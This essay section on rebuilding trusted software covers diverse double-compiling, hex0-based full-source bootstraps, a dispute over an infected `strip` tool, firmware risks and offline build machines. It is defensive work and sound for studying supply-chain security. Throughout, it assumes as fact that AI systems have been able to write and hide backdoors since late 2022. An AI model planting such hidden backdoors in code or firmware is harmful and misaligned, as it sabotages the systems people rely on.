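Diverse double-compiling, the subject of David A. Wheeler's 2009 dissertation, is a test for trusting-trust attacks that uses a second, unrelated compiler. Suppose the owner has a compiler binary from 2020 and its source code, and doesn't know whether the binary is infected. The test needs three builds, all from that same source code:

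| Build | Compiler that does the work | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The second compiler | A trial compiler |
| 2 | The trial compiler | Binary X |
| 3 | The suspect compiler | Binary Y |

The trial compiler will look different from the suspect one, because the second compiler picks different machine instructions for the same source code. But both should behave as that source code specifies, so they should translate any program identically. The owner then compares X with Y, which should match bit for bit.

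If the suspect compiler is infected, it adds the infection to Y. The trial compiler was never compiled with the suspect one, so it has no infection to add to X, and the two binaries differ. With Thompson's compiler, X would have been 10,724 bytes and Y 12,918.

A match doesn't prove that both compilers are clean. As Cox points out, they could both contain the same backdoor, though this is much less likely if different people wrote their source code separately. The second compiler can contain a different backdoor, as long as it doesn't affect the test. It can also be very slow and lack most features, since it only has to compile one program correctly. The owner could write a small one, as the programmers in Kesteloot's story did.

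The test also requires reproducible builds, because otherwise X and Y could differ in a harmless detail such as a date. The program that compares them and the operating system it runs on have to work correctly. The source code has to be clean too, because the test shows only that the binary matches its source code. A backdoor in the source code, like the one in InterBase, would be in both X and Y, and they would still match.

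If X and Y don't match, the owner knows that something is wrong but not which compiler is at fault. A third compiler could help identify it.

### Growing a system from a few hundred bytes

The owner can also avoid ready-made compilers and start with a program so small that a person can check every byte. The stage0 project starts with one called hex0, which reads pairs of hexadecimal digits (0 to 9 and A to F) and writes the corresponding bytes. For example, it turns the input `48 69` into the two bytes that spell "Hi".

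The source code of hex0 is a list of its own bytes as hexadecimal digits, with comments that explain them. Anyone with the processor's manual can check that the source code and the binary match, so Guix, a project that builds its own version of Linux, counts the binary as source code.

The rest of the system grows from there:

1. With hex0, the builder makes slightly better versions of the same tool, and then an assembler.
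2. The assembler makes M2-Planet, a compiler for a simple form of C.
3. M2-Planet makes Mes, which contains a fuller C compiler.
4. Mes makes the Tiny C Compiler.
5. The Tiny C Compiler makes an old version of GCC, the standard compiler on Linux, and that makes newer versions.

Four projects use such a chain, but they don't all start from the same point.

| Project | Seed | Processors | What has to be running first |
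|---|---|---|---|
| stage0 | hex0, a few hundred bytes | x86, ARM and RISC-V | An operating system |
| Guix | 357 bytes | x86 | Linux and Guix |
| Nixpkgs | 181 bytes | x86 | Linux and Nix |
| live-bootstrap | 512 bytes | 32-bit x86 | Only the firmware |

The x86 family includes most desktop and server processors from Intel and AMD. Published sizes of hex0 differ partly because programmers have kept shortening it. Guix's *The Full-Source Bootstrap* announced a collection of more than 22,000 packages, all descended from a 357-byte version that replaced about 250 megabytes of ready-made binaries. A contributor to Nixpkgs gives hex0's current size as 181 bytes, or 362 hexadecimal digits, which somebody could check by hand in a day or so.

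The "almost" in the headline of LWN's *The Guix (almost) full-source bootstrap* (2023) is justified because the 357 bytes run on an existing Linux kernel, and a compromised kernel could alter any file during the build. live-bootstrap (2020) removes this problem by starting without an operating system. Its 512-byte seed fills the first part of a disk, which the firmware loads when the computer starts. live-bootstrap then builds a very simple kernel, a better one called Fiwix, and finally Linux. stage0 posix, the documentation for stage0, therefore describes the problem as solved "up to the firmware level" and invites hardware developers to continue the work.

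In *A Full-Source Bootstrap for NixOS*, Jansen (2025) extended live-bootstrap to produce a working copy of NixOS. Three offline runs in a virtual machine on an ordinary desktop computer took between 17 and 18 hours each. The process also worked on a ThinkPad T440p, a laptop model from 2013. Most of the finished system came from source code, but the Rust compiler still came from a ready-made binary.

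Nixpkgs adopted a similar chain in January 2026. In *Nixpkgs Stdenv* (2026), a developer chat, one participant lists what they still need besides source code: an x86 machine with its firmware, a running Linux kernel, the Nix program and the seed. Rust and Go still start from binaries there too. An independent compiler can build Rust 1.74, but somebody would then have to build about twenty more versions in sequence to reach the current one. An owner who only wants a basic system from 2020 could leave Rust out, since the Linux kernel contained none at the time. Go is easier to build from source because version 1.4 is written in C, and anyone can build up to later versions from there.

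### The age of the instructions

None of these chains was complete in February 2020. The live-bootstrap project began that December, Guix finished its chain in 2023, and Nixpkgs followed in 2026. Anyone who uses the current instructions to rebuild a snapshot therefore relies on some text written after October 2022, the cautious cutoff for well-hidden AI-written backdoors.

The risk is smaller than it sounds, because the large programs in the middle of the chain are old. *Finding the Bottom Turtle* describes a route through GCC 2.95 (1999) and GCC 4.7 (2012), and the owner can take both from an archive that recorded their arrival. The newer parts are mostly small tools and build scripts, which a few people could read in full. live-bootstrap makes them easier to review by excluding pre-generated source code, such as long configure scripts that are rarely read.

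Somebody also has to use an ordinary computer to collect the source code and write it to a disk before the clean computer exists. live-bootstrap calls this an unsolved problem. If the ordinary computer is compromised, it could alter the files before they reach the disk. The bootstrap checks files against a list of hashes, but the list is on the same disk, so the owner should compare it with a copy printed earlier.

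Missing files can also stop the build. Jansen found that some source files had disappeared from their original addresses and others had different hashes, apparently because the websites hosting them had begun to pack them differently. Jansen had to take the missing files from the Nix project's store of earlier downloads. A recovery team might not have that option, so whoever keeps a snapshot should run the complete build in advance, without a network, and store every file it uses.

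### The dispute over small seeds

Programmers who discussed the `strip` experiment online in September 2026 disagreed with the researchers about how much a small seed helps. One critic quoted them as writing that a tampered `strip` keeps the infection going whenever it takes part in the build, even if the compiler seed shrinks to a few hundred bytes. The critic called this true but empty, since an infected tool obviously infects any build that uses it. A true bootstrap, the critic argued, starts with a few hundred bytes and builds everything else from source code, so no older copy of `strip` takes part. The quoted sentence doesn't appear in the conference version of the paper, which lists small seeds among the attempts to solve the problem at its root.

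The critic is right about a complete bootstrap. The attack needs an infected `strip` to exist before the build makes its own, and a chain that starts with hex0 has no earlier `strip`. Nixpkgs had merged its tiny x86 seed before the conference, so the attack as demonstrated no longer applies to the newest x86 version. Other processors still depended on larger seeds, although *A Full-Source Bootstrap for NixOS*, the NixOS forum discussion of Jansen's thesis, mentions early work on ARM and RISC-V.

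But the researchers' warning applies to anyone who replaces only the compiler. An owner who builds a clean compiler from hex0 and then uses the `strip` that came with an ordinary copy of Linux has let an untrusted binary back into the build. This is easy to do by accident, because a build may call dozens of utilities that nobody thinks about.

The owner also can't use the argument from definition to determine whether a particular build was a true bootstrap. The bootstrap in Nixpkgs runs on an existing kernel, and an infected kernel could do whatever the infected `strip` did. Another commenter noted that malware on a build machine can keep running in the background and alter the finished files at the end, without having to pass from one tool to the next.

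A similar disagreement arose over diverse double-compiling. According to *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation*, the test changes only the compiler, so the same infected `strip` would process both X and Y, and the comparison would show no difference. A commenter answered that Wheeler's method lets the tester change the whole environment, including the operating system and hardware. If X comes from a computer with an unrelated `strip`, the infection appears only in Y.

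Both descriptions are accurate, but they apply to different versions of the test. The owner should run the stronger version, in which the two sides share as little as possible. One side could use a complete Debian toolchain from 2019, and the other could be built up from hex0 on a different machine. If both sides produce the same compiler, an attacker could have tampered with it only by compromising both in matching ways.

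### What runs beneath the first instruction

A computer has already run a lot of code by the time it reads the first byte of hex0. Its firmware has prepared the memory, the keyboard and the screen. *Finding the Bottom Turtle* describes two more layers on x86 machines. System management mode lets firmware interrupt the operating system and run code that the operating system can't see. Below that, the Intel Management Engine and AMD's Platform Security Processor are small separate computers with access to the main one. Nunley adds microcode, which controls how the processor carries out its instructions, and the design of the chip itself.

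Disks have the same problem. Each contains a controller, a small computer whose firmware determines what the disk returns when the main processor requests a file. A compromised controller could return the correct file while somebody checks its hash, then an altered one when the machine next starts. In 2015 the security company Kaspersky described malware that could rewrite the firmware of disks from many well-known makers.

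A software archive can't supply any of these parts. It may contain the source code of some firmware, but the owner would still need a machine to build it on and a chip to run it on.

The essay's ideal solution is a computer that needs no firmware. Its first program would be physical, such as a pattern of wires, and its owner would use the computer to build the firmware for a better machine. Early computers came close, because people entered the first instructions with switches on the front panel. A computer without firmware would be far too slow to build Linux. The next step up might be a RISC-V or Power9 computer, because some of these can run almost entirely on open firmware.

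### Old machines and new ones

Most owners will have to choose between old computers from storage and new ones. As with software, an early enough date rules out AI-authored backdoors in hardware. If a laptop was made in 2013 and nobody has updated its firmware since 2019, the firmware can't contain one. A new machine's firmware could, because it dates from a time when AI could write and hide a backdoor.

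| | Stored machine from 2013 | New machine |
|---|---|---|
| Could its firmware contain an AI-authored backdoor? | No, if nobody has updated it | Yes |
| Does software from 2020 run on it? | Usually | Sometimes, with parts not working |
| Can it start live-bootstrap? | Usually | Often not |
| Can the owner get more of them? | Only second-hand | Yes |

The firmware's date also needs proof. A label shows the machine's manufacture date, but many computers install firmware updates automatically, so a laptop in daily use until last month is poor evidence of old firmware. One that has been switched off since 2019 is much better. Old firmware can contain implants written by people, just as old software can.

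Old hardware also solves the problem of missing drivers, the programs through which an operating system controls devices. A kernel from February 2020 has no drivers for devices that came later. For example, it can't start on a Mac with Apple's M1 processor, which went on sale that November. It will start on many newer PCs, because disks, keyboards and simple displays follow long-standing standards, but the wireless network or the graphics chip may not work. The owner could add a newer driver, but would then have to judge its source code like any other late addition.

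Jansen notes that live-bootstrap also needs a computer that can boot from a disk in the older way, which some newer machines no longer support. In that case, the owner can build an installer on an old machine and use it on the new ones.

Computers wear out even in storage. Batteries leak, capacitors dry out, fans seize, and the chips that hold the firmware slowly lose their charge. When the clock battery runs down, the machine may start with a date years in the past, and a build that records the date will produce a different binary. The owner should keep several machines of the same model for spare parts and start each one from time to time.

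There are also too few old machines, and they can't be copied the way snapshots can. So it makes more sense to use them for building and checking programs, and to run those programs on newer machines. The owner would then have clean programs on hardware that might still be compromised, which is better than having neither clean programs nor clean hardware.

Reproducible builds can reveal some compromised hardware. The owner runs the same build on an old Intel laptop, an old AMD desktop and a new machine, each with a disk from a different maker, and compares the binaries. If only one machine's firmware has tampered with the build, its binaries will differ from the others. This comparison doesn't detect firmware that leaves the build unchanged but steals passwords later.

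### Keeping the build machine offline

The build machine should never join a network. An old machine has the unpatched flaws of its time, so an intruder could take it over within minutes. A new one may have fewer known flaws, but if its firmware contains a backdoor, an intruder could send it instructions over the network. Removing all network hardware, including the wireless card, is safest because disabling it in a menu works only if the firmware applies the setting.

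Some tools make it hard to work offline. When Jansen first ran live-bootstrap from stored files, it failed unless the machine had a network card, because one step tried to get a network address. Jansen added an option to skip that step. On the ThinkPad, the last stage also failed without an internet connection, because NixOS had detected the laptop's hardware and turned on features that needed extra packages. This hadn't happened in a virtual machine rehearsal, so the owner should rehearse on the same model of computer they will use.

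Write-once discs are safer than memory sticks for moving finished programs to the computers that will use them, as long as the discs only travel away from the build machine. A memory stick contains a controller with its own firmware and can carry something back. Before installing anything, somebody can copy each disc's hash from the build machine's screen onto paper and compare it with the hash computed on the receiving computer.
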